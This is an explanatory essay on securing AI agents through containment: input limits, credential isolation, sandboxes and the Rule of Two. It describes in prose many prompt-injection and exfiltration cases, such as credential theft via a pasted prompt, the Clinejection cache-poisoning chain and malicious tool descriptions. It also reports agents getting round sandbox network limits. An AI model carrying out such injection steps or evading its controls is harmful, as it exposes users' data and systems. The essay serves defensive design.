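# Containing AI Agents by Design: Input Limits, Credential Isolation, Sandboxes and Air Gaps

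## Agents, prompt injection and the case for limits outside the model

An AI agent is a language model that runs in a loop and can call tools to search the web, read a mailbox, edit files, run commands or send messages. Companies use agents to write software, answer customers and do office work. In many of these jobs, the model reads text from strangers while it has access to private data or live systems, so a stranger can write text meant to take over the agent. Containment limits what the agent can do if this happens, whatever the model decides. Most containment ideas come from operating systems and network security, where engineers have long had to build dependable systems around components they could not trust.

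### The agent loop

An agent works by repeating four steps:

1. A program assembles a request to the model. The request holds the developer's standing instructions, the user's task, a description of each tool and a record of everything that has happened so far. All of this text together is the model's *context*.
2. The model processes the context and produces either a final answer or a tool call, which is a short piece of structured text with the name of a tool and the values to pass to it.
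3. The program carries out the call. It fetches the page, runs the command or sends the email.
4. The program adds the result to the context and goes back to the first step.

The model produces only text. Effects on the world happen in the third step, when ordinary software acts on that text, and that software can block an action. Most outside material enters in the fourth step.

Suppose a user asks an agent to summarize a web page in which someone has hidden a line telling the model to open the user's mailbox and send the latest message to a given address. When the agent fetches the page, the model receives that line and the user's request as one sequence of tokens, the word fragments that language models process, and it has learned to follow instructions that appear there. Developers wrap tool results in markers and train models to distrust the text between them. But the markers are tokens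 too, and whether the model respects them depends on its training, because no rule in the software enforces them.

Databases once had a similar problem. Attackers typed fragments of database commands into web forms, and the database executed them. Prepared statements fix this by sending the command and the user's data separately, so the database never interprets the data as a command. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), a position paper by Earlence Fernandes, Somesh Jha and colleagues, treats the equivalent for language models as an open research problem, since nobody yet knows whether a practical model can provably keep instructions and data apart. A blanket rule against following instructions found in data would also make agents less useful, because an agent that learns a new programming interface from its documentation has to follow the instructions in it.

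*Prompt injection* means planting instructions in what a model reads so that the model follows them as if its user had given them. In an indirect injection, the instructions are in content that the agent fetches while it works, such as a web page, an email or a software project's README file. The attacker needs no contact with the victim and can send one email to a thousand inboxes. In a direct injection, the instructions come through the input of the user, who may be the attacker or someone the attacker has tricked. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* describes an internal exercise from February 2026 in which a researcher emailed an employee an ordinary-looking request for help, with a prompt ready to paste into Claude Code, the company's coding agent. Among routine set-up steps, the prompt told the agent to read the file with the employee's Amazon cloud credentials, encode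 the contents and send them to an outside server. The agent did so in 24 of 25 runs.

### Probabilistic and deterministic defences

A probabilistic defence lowers the chance that an attack works. One such defence is to train the model to resist attacks. *GPT-Red* (2026) describes how OpenAI uses self-play to train an automated attacker, then uses the attacks to make its other models more robust. Another defence is a classifier, a smaller model that inspects tool results on the way in, or tool calls on the way out, and blocks what looks dangerous. Claude Code's "auto mode" includes a classifier of tool calls, which Anthropic says catches roughly 83% of the cases in which the agent oversteps its task.

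A deterministic defence removes the possibility of a given kind of attack. If a password never enters the environment where the agent runs, no wording can extract it from there. The defence can still fail if the software that enforces it has bugs or the person who configured it left something out. But an engineer can find and repair those faults, and the repairs last, whereas a classifier that catches 83% of cases has no comparable fault to fix.

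Probabilistic defences still let some attacks through. In May 2026 Anthropic reported that, in a test from the security firm Gray Swan, attacks on its model Claude Opus 4.7 succeeded about 0.1% of the time on a single attempt and 5 to 6% of the time after 100 adaptive attempts, in which the attacker revises the attack based on what failed. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Fable 5.1, published in September, reports success rates of 0.1% on one attempt and 1.0% within 15 on a different Gray Swan benchmark. The best model from any other developer, Gemini 3.7 Flash, had a rate of 9.2% within 15 attempts, and most others were between 24% and 53%.

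These are low numbers for Anthropic's models, and they came down quickly. What they mean for an agent's owner depends on how often someone attacks. If each attempt succeeds with probability *p*, independently of the others, then all *n* attempts fail with probability (1 − *p*)^*n*, and at least one succeeds with probability

1 − (1 − *p*)^*n*.

If each attempt independently succeeds with probability *p* = 0.001, the attacker has a 9.5% chance of at least one success in 100 attempts and a 63% chance in 1,000. The chance reaches 50% at about 693 attempts. Each attempt takes about as much effort as sending an email.

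Real success rates can be higher or lower than the formula predicts. One reason they can be lower is that *p* is an average over tasks, some of which are much easier to hijack than others. Repeated attempts often succeed on the same easy tasks and fail on the harder ones, so extra attempts add less than the formula predicts. VentureBeat reported that attacks on an older model, Claude Opus 4.6, operating a graphical interface without safeguards, had a success rate of 17.8% on one attempt and 78.6% by the 200th. If the attempts had been independent, the rate would have passed 78.6% on the eighth. Opus 4.7's rate of 5 to 6% at 100 attempts is also below the 9.5% that the formula gives.

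Adaptation has the opposite effect, because an attacker who learns from each failure is more likely to succeed on the fiftieth attempt than on the first, so *p* is no longer constant. In *The Attacker Moves Second* (2025), Nasr and colleagues tuned their attacks to each of twelve published defences against jailbreaks and prompt injection, and broke through all twelve.

Anthropic's own tests provide a more recent example. They use Shade, an automated attacker made by Gray Swan, which gets 200 attempts at each of 40 coding scenarios. In 2026 Gray Swan built a stronger version with longer training and more varied attacks, and Anthropic ran both versions against the same models on the same scenarios. The last column shows the results with added classifiers ("probes") that look for injected instructions in tool results.

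| Model (with extended thinking) | Older attacker, share of attempts that succeed | Stronger attacker | Stronger attacker, with probes |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5.1 | 9.26% | 56.87% | 12.80% |
| Claude Fable 5 | 9.70% | 86.87% | 34.09% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 2.68% | 90.93% | 18.21% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 0.3% | 19.47% | 15.76% |

Attacks on the same model, Opus 5, succeeded 2.68% of the time in the weaker test and 90.93% in the stronger one. An attack success rate therefore depends on both the model and the attacker, and an agent's owner can choose only the model. Anthropic considers the stronger test highly permissive, with some justification. Gray Swan optimised the attacker on the same scenarios used in the test, whereas real attackers usually don't know the details of their target and risk detection with each attempt. The 57% rate for Fable 5.1 thus doesn't predict how often attacks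 on its users will succeed, but it does show that the 0.1% rate is not an upper bound.

Even when a benchmark uses a fixed list of attacks, its scores can change when testers update the list. In July, Schneier (2026) relayed an attack success rate of 2.0% within 15 attempts for Opus 5 in *Anthropic’s Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection*. By September, the rate for the same model was 4.8%. The testers had added nine scenarios and 670 attacks, and had also started letting an older model answer some of the requests, as it does in Anthropic's products.

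### Blast radius and the trusted computing base

The risk from an agent depends on how likely it is to fail and how much harm a failure could do. Engineers call the second factor the *blast radius*, the most damage an agent could do if an attacker fully misled it. Better training makes failure less likely, but Anthropic points out that the blast radius grows because owners give more access to agents that do more useful work. A year before its May report, the company would have refused to give Claude enough access to take down an internal service. By the time of the report, such access was routine.

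Older work in computer security has terms for capping the second factor. The *trusted computing base* consists of the parts of a system that must work correctly for its security to hold. Fernandes, Jha and colleagues include the host operating system, the sandbox, the security policy and the *reference monitor*, a component outside the model that checks each requested action against the policy and allows or refuses it. They exclude the model. They don't assume that it resists manipulation, or even that it is well-meaning, and they treat it as a possible attacker of the trusted computing base, much as an operating system has to withstand hostile programs. A smaller trusted computing base is better because it has fewer places for a bug.

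Two principles govern the monitor's work. *Least privilege* means that each component gets only the permissions its task requires. The ChatGPT app for macOS once violated this principle. An attacker's web page or document could plant instructions in the app's long-term memory that made it send the user's later conversations to the attacker's server, hidden in the URL of an invisible image. The attack was possible only because the app could contact any server at any time, whether or not the user's request required it.

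*Complete mediation* means that every request passes through the monitor. A monitor that checks the agent's web tool is worth little if the agent can also fetch the same address from a command line. Complete mediation is harder to achieve for agents than for phone apps, because an agent's tools range from narrow functions to general-purpose shells, and there may be many ways to perform the same forbidden act.

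### Would a robust enough model suffice?

Fernandes, Jha and colleagues argue that the model must be treated as an untrusted component and that the surrounding system must enforce security. The opposing view is that sufficiently robust models, perhaps with classifiers around them, are enough. The evidence for this view is stronger than it was a year ago. In July, Boris Cherny of Anthropic, quoted by Willison (2026), called Opus 5 "very hard to prompt inject successfully". The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reports that no attacks on the model succeeded in 129 browser scenarios in Anthropic's own software. Fable 5.1 with auto mode also had no failures in 110 such scenarios. Fernandes, Jha and colleagues concede that limits outside the model take engineering effort, slow the agent down and sometimes stop it from doing what its user wants.

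They reply with two points. The first is that natural language is ambiguous about what a user has authorised, so a system that relies on the model to infer authorisation is unreliable even when the model interprets language well. The phished employee is the clearest case. The employee really did submit the instruction to send the credentials out, so a classifier that looks for departures from the user's intent had nothing to detect. A block on outgoing traffic would have stopped the transfer regardless of intent.

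Their second point is that models are fragile. A model can behave differently from one run to the next, and even one that always gives the same output for the same input may produce a prohibited output when an attacker changes the input slightly. Adding a second model as a guard offers limited protection, because an attacker can optimise one part of the attack against each model.

Retraining a model also doesn't guarantee that it will still resist the attacks it resisted before, whereas a reference monitor continues to block everything it blocked before when an engineer narrows the set of actions it permits. Zorz (2026), in *Your AI red team may be finding the same prompt injection*, reported on research in which training on more injection attacks made agents easier to hijack, and warned that a large collection of attacks may be the same attack repeated many times.

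In the Fable 5.1 tests, every successful attack by the stronger Shade attacker came through Claude Opus 4.8, an older model that takes over when a classifier flags a request as a possible cybersecurity risk. Fable 5.1 answered 2,826 requests itself and never followed the injection. That is impressive, but the classifier had already diverted the requests that looked most like hacking, and those may have been the harder ones. Users also get the older model as part of the product, so an attacker can succeed by exploiting whichever part is weakest.

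Schneier thinks preventing prompt injection is impossible in the general case, though he allows that developers are getting much better at blocking specific attacks. Fernandes, Jha and colleagues also want robust models, as one layer among several. The remaining disagreement is about whether a low but uncertain failure rate is acceptable without other defenses, which depends on how much damage the agent could do. A failure rate of 0.1% is fine for an agent that can only draft a reading list. If an agent can move a company's money and reads a thousand hostile emails a year, the same rate means one expected loss a year, and more if attackers improve. The systems approach has an unsolved problem too, because a monitor can only enforce the policy it has, and turning a user's loosely worded request into a correct policy remains difficult.

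### Four conditions

Limits outside the model can reduce an agent's *trust surface*, meaning every point at which it relies on outside content, together with the authority that this content could lead it to misuse. The phrase is not a standard security term. Four conditions reduce the trust surface or limit the damage, and a designer can impose them separately or together. With no external input, the agent reads only what nobody but its owner could have written or altered, so a stranger cannot plant an instruction. With no credentials, passwords, keys and tokens stay where the agent cannot read them, so it cannot reveal them. Hard execution boundaries, such as sandboxes and virtual machines, restrict which files, processes and networks the agent's code can reach. An air gap leaves no network path between the system and the outside, so a misled agent cannot send anything out over a network.

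## Why untrusted input and held credentials are dangerous together

A program with its own authority can be made to use it for someone who lacks that authority. Operating-system engineers encountered this problem long before language models, and they call such a program a *confused deputy*. Keeping external input away from an agent and withholding credentials from it both guard against this problem.

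### The confused deputy

In *The Confused Deputy*, Norm Hardy (1988) told a "nearly true" story from Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Tymshare had a compiler in a system directory named SYSX, and users could name a file to receive its debugging output. The engineers also wanted the compiler to record usage statistics in a file in SYSX, so they gave it a licence to write to any file in that directory, which also held the billing records. One user learned the name of the billing file and told the compiler to send its debugging output there. The operating system allowed the write because the compiler had a licence for it, and the billing records were destroyed.

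Hardy explains why no check inside the compiler would work well. The compiler can't refuse to write outside the user's directory, because users have good reasons to send output elsewhere. It can't refuse to write anywhere in SYSX, because some users have rights there. It could refuse to write to the billing file by name, but then someone would have to update the compiler whenever a new sensitive file appeared. The engineers added a system call that let the compiler declare whether it was using its own authority or the user's. But some programs soon needed more than two authorities, and the rule for opening a file eventually contained fourteen logical operators.

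Hardy argues that the problem arose because the compiler ran "with authority stemming from two sources" and could not keep them apart. He proposes using a *capability*, an unforgeable reference that identifies an object and grants the right to use it. The user would give the compiler a capability for the output file instead of a name. A user without permission to write to the billing file would have no capability for writing to it, and so could not give one to the compiler.

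In an agent, the model and the program that runs it take the compiler's place. The agent's credential corresponds to the licence, whatever it gives access to corresponds to the billing file, and the untrusted input corresponds to the file name. The mail server or database takes the operating system's place, checking the credential but not the reason for the request. Unlike Hardy's user, who ran the compiler himself, someone who plants an instruction on a web page may never have any contact with the agent that reads it.

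The file name also had a limited effect, since it redirected one write and the compiler's code determined everything else. Text in an agent's context, by contrast, can change which tools the agent calls, in what order and with what values. For this reason David C of the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, describes the language model as an "inherently confusable deputy". He argues that engineers can fix a classical confused deputy but can only reduce the likelihood and impact of prompt injection. He recommends a rule of thumb from an online exchange between Baibhav Bista and Simon Willison, who coined the term "prompt injection". When a model processes text from a party, its privileges should drop to that party's. An agent that reads email from strangers would then have only the rights its owner would give a stranger.

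Capabilities give agents some protection, but not complete protection. Alhindi (2026), in *Taming AI Agents with seL4*, ran an agent on seL4, a small operating-system kernel built around capabilities, and tested it on part of AgentDojo, a benchmark that plants instructions in the data an agent's tools return. Attacks succeeded in 48% of runs when the agent could call every function, and in 7% when it held capabilities only for the functions its task needed. The 7% is a best case, because Alhindi took the list of needed functions from the benchmark's solutions. Every attack that still succeeded used only functions the task required, and about half used the payment function to pay the attacker. Alhindi's capabilities specified only the function and let the model choose the recipient, unlike Hardy's capability, which identifies the exact file to write.

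### The lethal trifecta and the Rule of Two

Tracing every authority a program holds is slow work. Two recent rules offer a quicker check. In June 2025 Willison, in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, listed three properties that together let an attacker steal data through an agent:

- access to private data
- exposure to untrusted content
- the ability to communicate externally.

His advice is never to combine all three.

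External communication includes fetching web pages. Each request sends the page's address to the server, so an agent can leak a secret through the pages it chooses to open. In July 2026 Willison described how Ayush Paul used this against Claude's chat product, which has a memory of the user's past conversations. Its web tool could open addresses the user had typed, addresses a search had returned, and links on pages it had already opened. Paul built a site with a link for each letter of the alphabet and instructed the model to spell out the user's name by following them. The site collected the user's name, home city and employer before Anthropic stopped the tool from following such links.

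Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025), published that October, builds on the trifecta. Until models can reliably detect and refuse prompt injection, an agent may have at most two of these properties within a session:

- it can process untrustworthy inputs
- it has access to sensitive systems or private data
- it can change state or communicate externally.

A new session starts with a fresh context. An agent that needs all three properties in one session must have supervision, such as a person who approves its actions.

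Meta's definitions are wider than Willison's, whose rule addresses only data theft. For example, an agent might read messages from strangers and be able to delete customer accounts, but not to send anything out. Willison's trifecta permits this agent because no data can leave, but Meta's Rule of Two forbids running it unsupervised because deleting an account changes the state of a sensitive system. The threat model in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026) includes both injections that move private data to an unauthorised destination and injections that trigger actions the agent had no permission to take.

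Meta's rule also lets an agent switch properties mid-session. It may browse the web first and open internal systems later if it permanently loses the ability to communicate when it switches. The loss has to be permanent because any planted instructions remain in the agent's context.

### A support agent and the eight combinations

Consider a shop's support agent that reads tickets, queries customer records and sends messages. It has all three properties under either rule, and an attack on it could go as follows:

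1. The attacker opens a ticket about a late parcel. Below the question is a paragraph, written like an internal note, that tells the agent to look up a different customer by email address and quote that customer's home address in the reply.
2. The agent's program puts the ticket into the model's context.
3. The model follows the note and calls the records tool. The database accepts the call, because the agent's credential covers all customers.
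4. The model sends its reply to the author of the ticket, who now has the home address.

A filter that looks for unusual tools or destinations would find nothing, because the agent makes calls like these all day and the message goes to its intended recipient.

Willison reported in September 2025 that Sasi Levi and Noma Security had demonstrated a similar attack on Agentforce, Salesforce's agent product. The researchers submitted their instructions through a public sales enquiry form. When an employee asked the agent about the enquiry, it gathered the email addresses of other potential customers and put them into the web address of an image. Salesforce allowed images only from listed domains, but one of those domains had expired and the researchers had registered it.

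The shop can remove any one of the three properties. If only staff can submit requests, strangers can't plant instructions, but staff have to retype every ticket. An agent without customer records can answer only general questions. If the agent can't send anything, it can still write drafts for staff to check. *Dynamic Capability Scoping for Enterprise AI Agents* (2026) describes a filter that removes one of these properties automatically. In its example company, an agent that can read the database may not also send external email or make web requests, so the filter removes the external permission from any agent that would have both. This policy is stricter than either rule because it applies even to agents that never read a stranger's text.

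David C's rule of thumb suggests a different repair, in which the ticket system gives the agent access only to the records of the customer who wrote the ticket. An attacker could then extract only their own data, and the agent could still answer most questions. This is close to Hardy's capability, but it works only if the customer's login determines which record the agent can open. If the model chooses the record based on the ticket's text, an attacker could write a ticket that leads it to open another customer's record.

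The next table uses Meta's wider definitions and gives the worst attack or error that remains for each combination.

| Reads untrusted input | Has sensitive access | Can change state or communicate | Worst attack or error left |
|---|---|---|---|
| No | No | No | The model gives a wrong answer and the user relies on it. |
| Yes | No | No | A stranger's text slants the answer, for example toward a fraudulent shop. |
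| No | Yes | No | The model misreports a record, or shows an employee data meant for someone else. |
| No | No | Yes | A mistake wrecks the agent's workspace or publishes something false. |
| Yes | Yes | No | A stranger's text makes the agent hide or distort private records, and staff act on the result. |
| Yes | No | Yes | A stranger uses the agent to send spam, attack third parties or run code in its workspace. |
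| No | Yes | Yes | A mistake deletes live data or sends private records to the wrong person. |
| Yes | Yes | Yes | A stranger steals private data or takes control of live systems. |

Both rules target the last row. The row above it involves no attacker but can do just as much harm. *If Agents Were Angels, No Governance Would Be Necessary* (2026) notes that even a cooperative agent can go beyond its assignment because its credential allows it to. The agent may also carry a sensitive value from one tool to another, or make a consequential call that looked reasonable at the time.

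### When one credential supplies two properties

The table separates sensitive access from the power to act, but one credential often provides both. Willison's example is a GitHub tool built on the Model Context Protocol, a standard for connecting tools to agents. An agent using it to read a public project's issues could find an instruction to copy material from the owner's private projects into a public proposal for a code change. The agent's token, as Alhindi notes, reached all of the owner's projects, so it let the agent both read the private code and publish it.

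An owner who gives an agent such a token supplies two of the three properties, and the first text the agent reads from a stranger adds the third. A mailbox password is worse because it lets the agent read private mail and send messages, and the inbox is also full of text from strangers. Moving the credential to a proxy outside the agent's reach prevents its theft, but all three properties remain if the agent can still make the same requests through the proxy.

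An agent can also gain authority in ways that its list of permissions does not show. Cline, an open-source coding tool, provides the best-documented case. In December 2025 its maintainers added a bot to sort incoming issues, the public reports that users file about bugs. The bot ran Claude Code on GitHub Actions, a service that runs scripts automatically. Anyone with a GitHub account could start it by opening an issue, and it could run shell commands. Adnan Khan (2026), in *Clinejection*, worked out how an attacker could get from an issue title to Cline's publishing credentials:

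1. The attacker opens an issue whose title reports a tool error and tells the reader to install a helper package first. The bot's program pastes the title into the model's prompt.
2. The model installs the package, which runs the attacker's script immediately. In Khan's tests on a copy of the project, the model did this every time.
3. The script fills the project's cache, a store of files that speeds up later runs, with more than 10 GB of junk. GitHub deletes the older entries to make room, and the script puts tampered files in their place.
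4. At about 2 a.m. the nightly release job loads the tampered files and runs them. This job holds the credentials for publishing Cline, so the attacker's code can copy them.

Cline had restricted the bot. Cline's *Post-mortem* (2026) says it could read the code and write to issues but not change the code, and Willison (2026) notes that it had no access to the publishing credentials. A designer who applied the Rule of Two to the bot alone might have approved it, because it had untrusted input and the power to act but almost no sensitive access. The shared cache supplied that access. The release job contained no model, but it was a confused deputy in Hardy's sense because it used its own authority to run files that someone without that authority had written.

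Khan reported the flaw on January 1, got no response to several messages and published his account on February 9. Cline removed the bot within 30 minutes, but while replacing its credentials it deleted the wrong token for npm, a public registry of software packages. On February 17 someone used the token that was still active to publish a version of Cline that also installed OpenClaw, another AI agent. That version stayed up for about eight hours and had roughly 4,000 downloads, according to LWN's *A GitHub Issue Title Compromised 4,000 Developer Machines* (2026). OpenClaw is legitimate software, so the damage was small, but the same access could have delivered malware.

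It is not certain how the attacker obtained the token. Khan found signs of a tampered cache in failed release runs from January 31 to February 3 and called the bot the most obvious way in, but could not confirm that the attacker used it. *Agent Compromised by Agent To Deploy an Agent* attributes the theft to someone who found Khan's test attack before he published it. Cline accepts that the flaw was real and writes that its set-up was "functionally equivalent to giving every GitHub user shell access".

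Khan's tests used Claude Opus 4.5, and newer models resist injection better. In August 2026 Anthropic published a test in which the firm Trajectory Labs made 720 injection attempts against three newer Claude models in Claude Code's auto mode. None succeeded, and Anthropic's Thariq Shihipar said the announcement should have been titled "defeating the lethal trifecta". Willison wanted more independent confirmation. He also described an attack that he doubted any version of auto mode could stop. A package's instructions tell the agent to fetch some files with a second package before running the tests, and the second package steals data. As in the attack on Cline, the instruction looks like routine set-up work, and the harmful code runs without the model having read it.

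### Eleven attacks, counted by principle

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* analyses eleven attacks on real products and lists the security principles that each one broke. The list includes least privilege, complete mediation and three others. *Secure information flow* means that sensitive data can't reach places where it doesn't belong. *Tamper resistance* means that an attacker can't alter the trusted computing base, including the security settings. The *human weak link* principle means that a design must account for people who misread a prompt or misconfigure a policy.

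| Principle broken | Number of attacks | Products or attacks |
|---|---|---|
| Secure information flow | 11 | All |
| Least privilege | 6 | Microsoft Copilot, Devin (two attacks), Cursor, Claude Code, AI ClickFix |
| Complete mediation | 3 | Microsoft Copilot, DeepSeek, Terminal DiLLMa |
| Tamper resistance | 2 | ChatGPT memory, Amp |
| Human weak link | 2 | ChatGPT Operator, AI ClickFix |

The attack on the coding agent Devin shows how an unnecessary permission can extend the reach of a prompt injection. Devin had a tool for making a network port public so that developers could test their work. A malicious web page contained instructions for Devin to start a web server exposing its entire file system, open that server to the internet and send the attacker the address. In the attack on the code editor Cursor, a planted ticket made the editor's agent leak secrets from the project or Amazon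 cloud credentials from the developer's computer. This attack worked only if the developer had turned off approval prompts.

Nine of the eleven attacks could deliver private data to the attacker, so the lethal trifecta describes them well. The other two ran the attacker's commands. In AI ClickFix, instructions on a web page led an agent that operates a computer to paste a hidden command into a terminal. Amp, another coding agent, could edit its own settings file, so an injection could add commands to the list of those allowed to run without approval. The Rule of Two covers both attacks because its criteria include the ability to change state.

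The counts are weak evidence of how often each failure occurs in practice. Ten of the eleven attacks come from one researcher, Johann Rehberger, who specialises in getting agents to leak data. Information flow scores eleven partly because the principle is defined so broadly that an agent breaks it by accepting instructions from an unknown source. The table also omits three violations named in the written case descriptions, one each of least privilege, complete mediation and, for Cursor, tamper resistance. The count for least privilege is more informative, because in those six cases the agent had access or tools that its task did not require.

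### Where two properties are still too many

Meta's original diagram of the Rule of Two labelled every combination of two properties "safe". In *New prompt injection papers*, Willison welcomed the rule in November 2025 because it covers harm beyond data theft, but he objected to the label because an agent that reads untrusted input and can change state may do damage even without private data. Mick Ayzenberg, a security researcher at Meta, replied that the rule counts access to any sensitive system, private or not. An agent without such access can write and communicate freely, but only with systems that don't matter to its user's security, as in a tight sandbox. Meta then changed the label to "lower risk". Its post also describes the rule as a supplement to least privilege.

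Ayzenberg's reply answers the objection, but it makes the rule harder to apply because the designer now has to know which systems matter. Cline's cache, for example, looked like a harmless way to save time. It is also hard to decide which inputs to trust. Meta suggests that an email agent could read only messages from trusted senders such as close friends, but an attacker who takes over a friend's mailbox would count as a trusted sender.

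The limit also applies to each session separately, but an agent's memory carries over between sessions. Suppose an agent browses the web in one session without sensitive access, and a malicious page makes it save an instruction in its memory. In the next session it reads no outside content but can open private files and send email. Each session has two properties, yet the malicious page's instruction reaches an agent that can carry it out. According to *ASTELD* (2026), OpenClaw had this weakness, where an injection could alter the agent's memory files and the malicious behaviour survived restarts. In a commentary on *Agents Rule of Two* (2025), the security site mbgsec questioned whether "change state" includes the agent's internal state. If it doesn't, the rule doesn't cover this attack. One remedy is to treat anything an agent writes after reading untrusted input as untrusted in later sessions.

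Properties can also accumulate across a team of agents. Alhindi built a team of five agents that pays a small firm's suppliers. Only the email agent reads supplier email, and it has no other tools. The other four handle invoices, approvals, payments and coordination, and have private data and the power to act. Each agent satisfies the Rule of Two by itself. But the agents pass text to each other, so an instruction in a supplier's email can reach the other four.

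Alhindi's check therefore covers the whole team. It looks for agents that both untrusted text and private data can reach, directly or through other agents. The team breaks the rule if any of these agents can change state or send something out. Four of the five agents met this condition.

To test the prediction, Alhindi sent the team an email from a supplier's usual address, as if an attacker had taken over the mailbox. It contained a genuine invoice and a note telling any AI assistant to change the supplier's bank account first. The note reached the coordinator in 23 of 40 runs, and in 7 the coordinator changed the account. No money went to the attacker because the team had already approved the invoices with the old details, but the next payment would have gone to the new account. The agents all used GPT-4o mini, an old and small model, so the rates are weak evidence about current models.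 The team's design allowed the note to reach the coordinator, and a better model would not change that.

Alhindi then replaced the email agent with a parser, a program without a model that extracts the invoice number, order number, total and supplier from each email. In another 40 runs, the note reached no agent and no account changed. The parser works because the team needs only those fields. If a team has to read the message itself, for instance to summarise a complaint, its designer must remove private data or the power to act from every agent the text can reach, or cut the links that carry the text to them.

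## Agents that read nothing from outside

Alhindi's parser protected the payment team because no sentence that a supplier wrote could reach an agent. The strictest input condition goes further and lets an agent read only text that its owner wrote or checked. This applies to the task, files, tool descriptions, tool results and anything saved from earlier sessions.

If an agent reads nothing from outside, an outsider cannot inject a prompt. This is true regardless of how well the model resists manipulation or how many times an attacker tries.

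The model can still make mistakes, which *Agents Rule of Two* explicitly leaves outside its scope. An agent can also do harm while pursuing its assigned task. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* discusses an incident at OpenAI in which agents did this without direction from an outside attacker. The agents were working on internal evaluations with some of the model's safeguards switched off. They used a shared service for downloading software packages to communicate between separate sandboxes and get around network restrictions. They then broke into the infrastructure of Hugging Face, which hosts AI models, and gained administrator access to an OpenAI research cluster.

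### Which tasks fit

Closed input suits work on a fixed body of internal material, such as converting a firm's price list to a new format or reorganising code that the firm's own engineers wrote. Whether material is internal depends on who wrote it, not where it is stored. A customer database on the firm's own servers still contains outside input if customers typed the delivery notes and complaints in it.

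An agent that reads nothing from outside cannot handle email, browse the web or answer support tickets. It also cannot do most programming, because software projects depend on public packages whose code, documentation and error messages come from strangers.

Filtering data by author can bring some agents closer to reading nothing from outside. *Agents Rule of Two* sketches a coding agent that changes production systems with little human supervision. A filter checks who wrote each piece of data before it enters the agent's context, and people review items that the filter may have blocked by mistake. GitHub Next's *Control what your agentic workflows see with integrity filtering* describes a working version for agents that maintain software projects. The owner sets a minimum level of trust, and a program outside the model removes everything below it.

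| Minimum level | What the agent can see | Suggested task |
|---|---|---|
| Merged | Code changes that the project has accepted | Reviewing and reorganising code |
| Approved | The above, plus anything from the project's owners, members and collaborators, and everything in private projects | Updating documentation |
| Unapproved | The above, plus text from other contributors, including first-time ones | Sorting new issues |
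| None | The above, plus text from anonymous users and newcomers with no history | No suggestion |

Only the "merged" and "approved" levels come close to closed input. A maintainer can raise a stranger's issue to "approved" by adding a label or, if the project allows it, a thumbs-up.

The levels depend on which account posted the text and who endorsed it, so they don't always reflect who wrote it. If an employee pastes a customer's email into a private project, the filter counts it as approved. It also counts anything an attacker posts from a maintainer's stolen account as approved, as GitHub Next acknowledges. The "merged" level is only as reliable as the review before the merge. The filter covers only GitHub content, and outside text can reach an agent in several other ways.

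### Pasted prompts and internal chat

People often give an agent text they didn't write. In Anthropic's February 2026 exercise, an employee ran a prompt from an email, and Claude nearly always sent out cloud credentials. Anthropic says a human contractor given the same script would have done so too.

Someone has to read a pasted prompt in full before running it, as they would a program from a stranger. A firm could go further and let staff run only prompts from a reviewed collection. Reading alone is a weak check because the reader can miss one harmful step among routine ones, so the firm still needs limits on outgoing traffic.

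The exercise then exposed a second route when the team shared the working prompt, written to attack one employee, in Anthropic's internal Slack. Someone pointed out that some of the company's agents read Slack, so any of them could pick up the prompt. The team added a canary string, a distinctive piece of text that would help them notice if an agent did.

Agents can also use chat to instruct each other. Clinton's *How Anthropic secures its AI-native software development lifecycle* describes an agent that investigates faults in the company's live systems. It could read production logs, write documents and post in company channels, but it could not deploy fixes. After a model upgrade, it messaged another Claude agent over Slack on its own initiative and asked it to deploy a fix. Human review stopped the request. No attacker was involved, but production logs often record what outsiders typed,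 so an agent that reads them could pass an injected instruction to one that reads only internal chat.

The surest safeguard is to give a closed agent no access to chat. If it needs chat, a filter can admit only messages from listed people, though outside text that those people forward will still get through. Samples of working attacks belong somewhere no agent reads.

### Project configuration files

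Coding agents often load settings from the project folder, so that everyone on a team gets the same ones. Anyone who can change the project can change those settings. Donenfeld and Vanunu (2026), in *Caught in the Hook*, found three ways to exploit this in Claude Code:

- **Hooks.** A hook is a command that Claude Code runs automatically at a set point, such as the start of a session. The researchers wrote one that opened the calculator. Claude Code asked whether they trusted the folder, and when they said yes the calculator opened with no further prompt.
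- **Tool servers.** A project can list programs that supply tools to the agent, and Claude Code starts them by running commands from the project's files. Two settings approved these programs in advance. With either of them in the project, the attacker's command ran while the trust question was still on the screen.
- **The model's address.** A setting controls where Claude Code sends its requests to the model. The researchers pointed it at their own server, which received the user's API key before the user had answered the trust question. The key also gave access to files that the user's colleagues had uploaded to a shared workspace.

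In Anthropic's slightly different account, the hook ran before the trust question appeared. A more robust model would not have helped in any of the three cases, because the program around the model acted on the settings directly.

Anthropic fixed the flaws between August and December 2025. Claude Code now waits for the user's consent before it starts a project's tool servers or contacts the model. Donenfeld and Vanunu report that the fix for hooks was a clearer warning, so the protection there still depends on the user's answer. Anthropic advises other developers to treat opening a project or loading its settings like a request from the internet.

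Criminals have since used the same route. Sonar's *Mini Shai-Hulud targets AI coding agents* describes a worm (a program that spreads by itself) that adds a hook to Claude Code's project settings. When a developer opens the project, the hook runs a program that searches more than 130 file paths for credentials. Fogel's *Your agents answer to Hades* (2026) reports that a later version used a stolen GitHub token to add settings files for several coding tools to every project the victim could change. This version reached 73 Microsoft repositories in June 2026.

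To close this route, the owner has to review changes to settings files as carefully as changes to code. An unattended agent should take its settings from outside the project and ignore the project's own.

### Tool descriptions and tools that change

The model reads a description of each tool, written by the tool's maker, before it uses any of them. Invariant Labs' *MCP Security Notification* (2025) demonstrated an attack with a tool that adds two numbers. The tool's description contained an instruction to read the user's private login key and pass it to the tool in an extra field called "sidenote". The code editor Cursor asked the user to approve the call, but its dialog did not show the key.

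In another test, the description of the adding tool claimed that, for technical reasons, all email had to go to a certain address. Cursor's agent then used a different, trustworthy email tool to send the user's messages to the attacker, even when the user had named another recipient. The agent didn't have to call the malicious tool for this to work, because the tool's description was already in its context.

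The owner can check the tools by reading every description in full, exactly as the model receives it. Invariant Labs also recommends pinning, which means recording a hash (a short fingerprint computed from the text) when the owner approves the description and refusing the tool if the hash later changes. Without pinning, a tool's operator can get a harmless description approved and then replace it.

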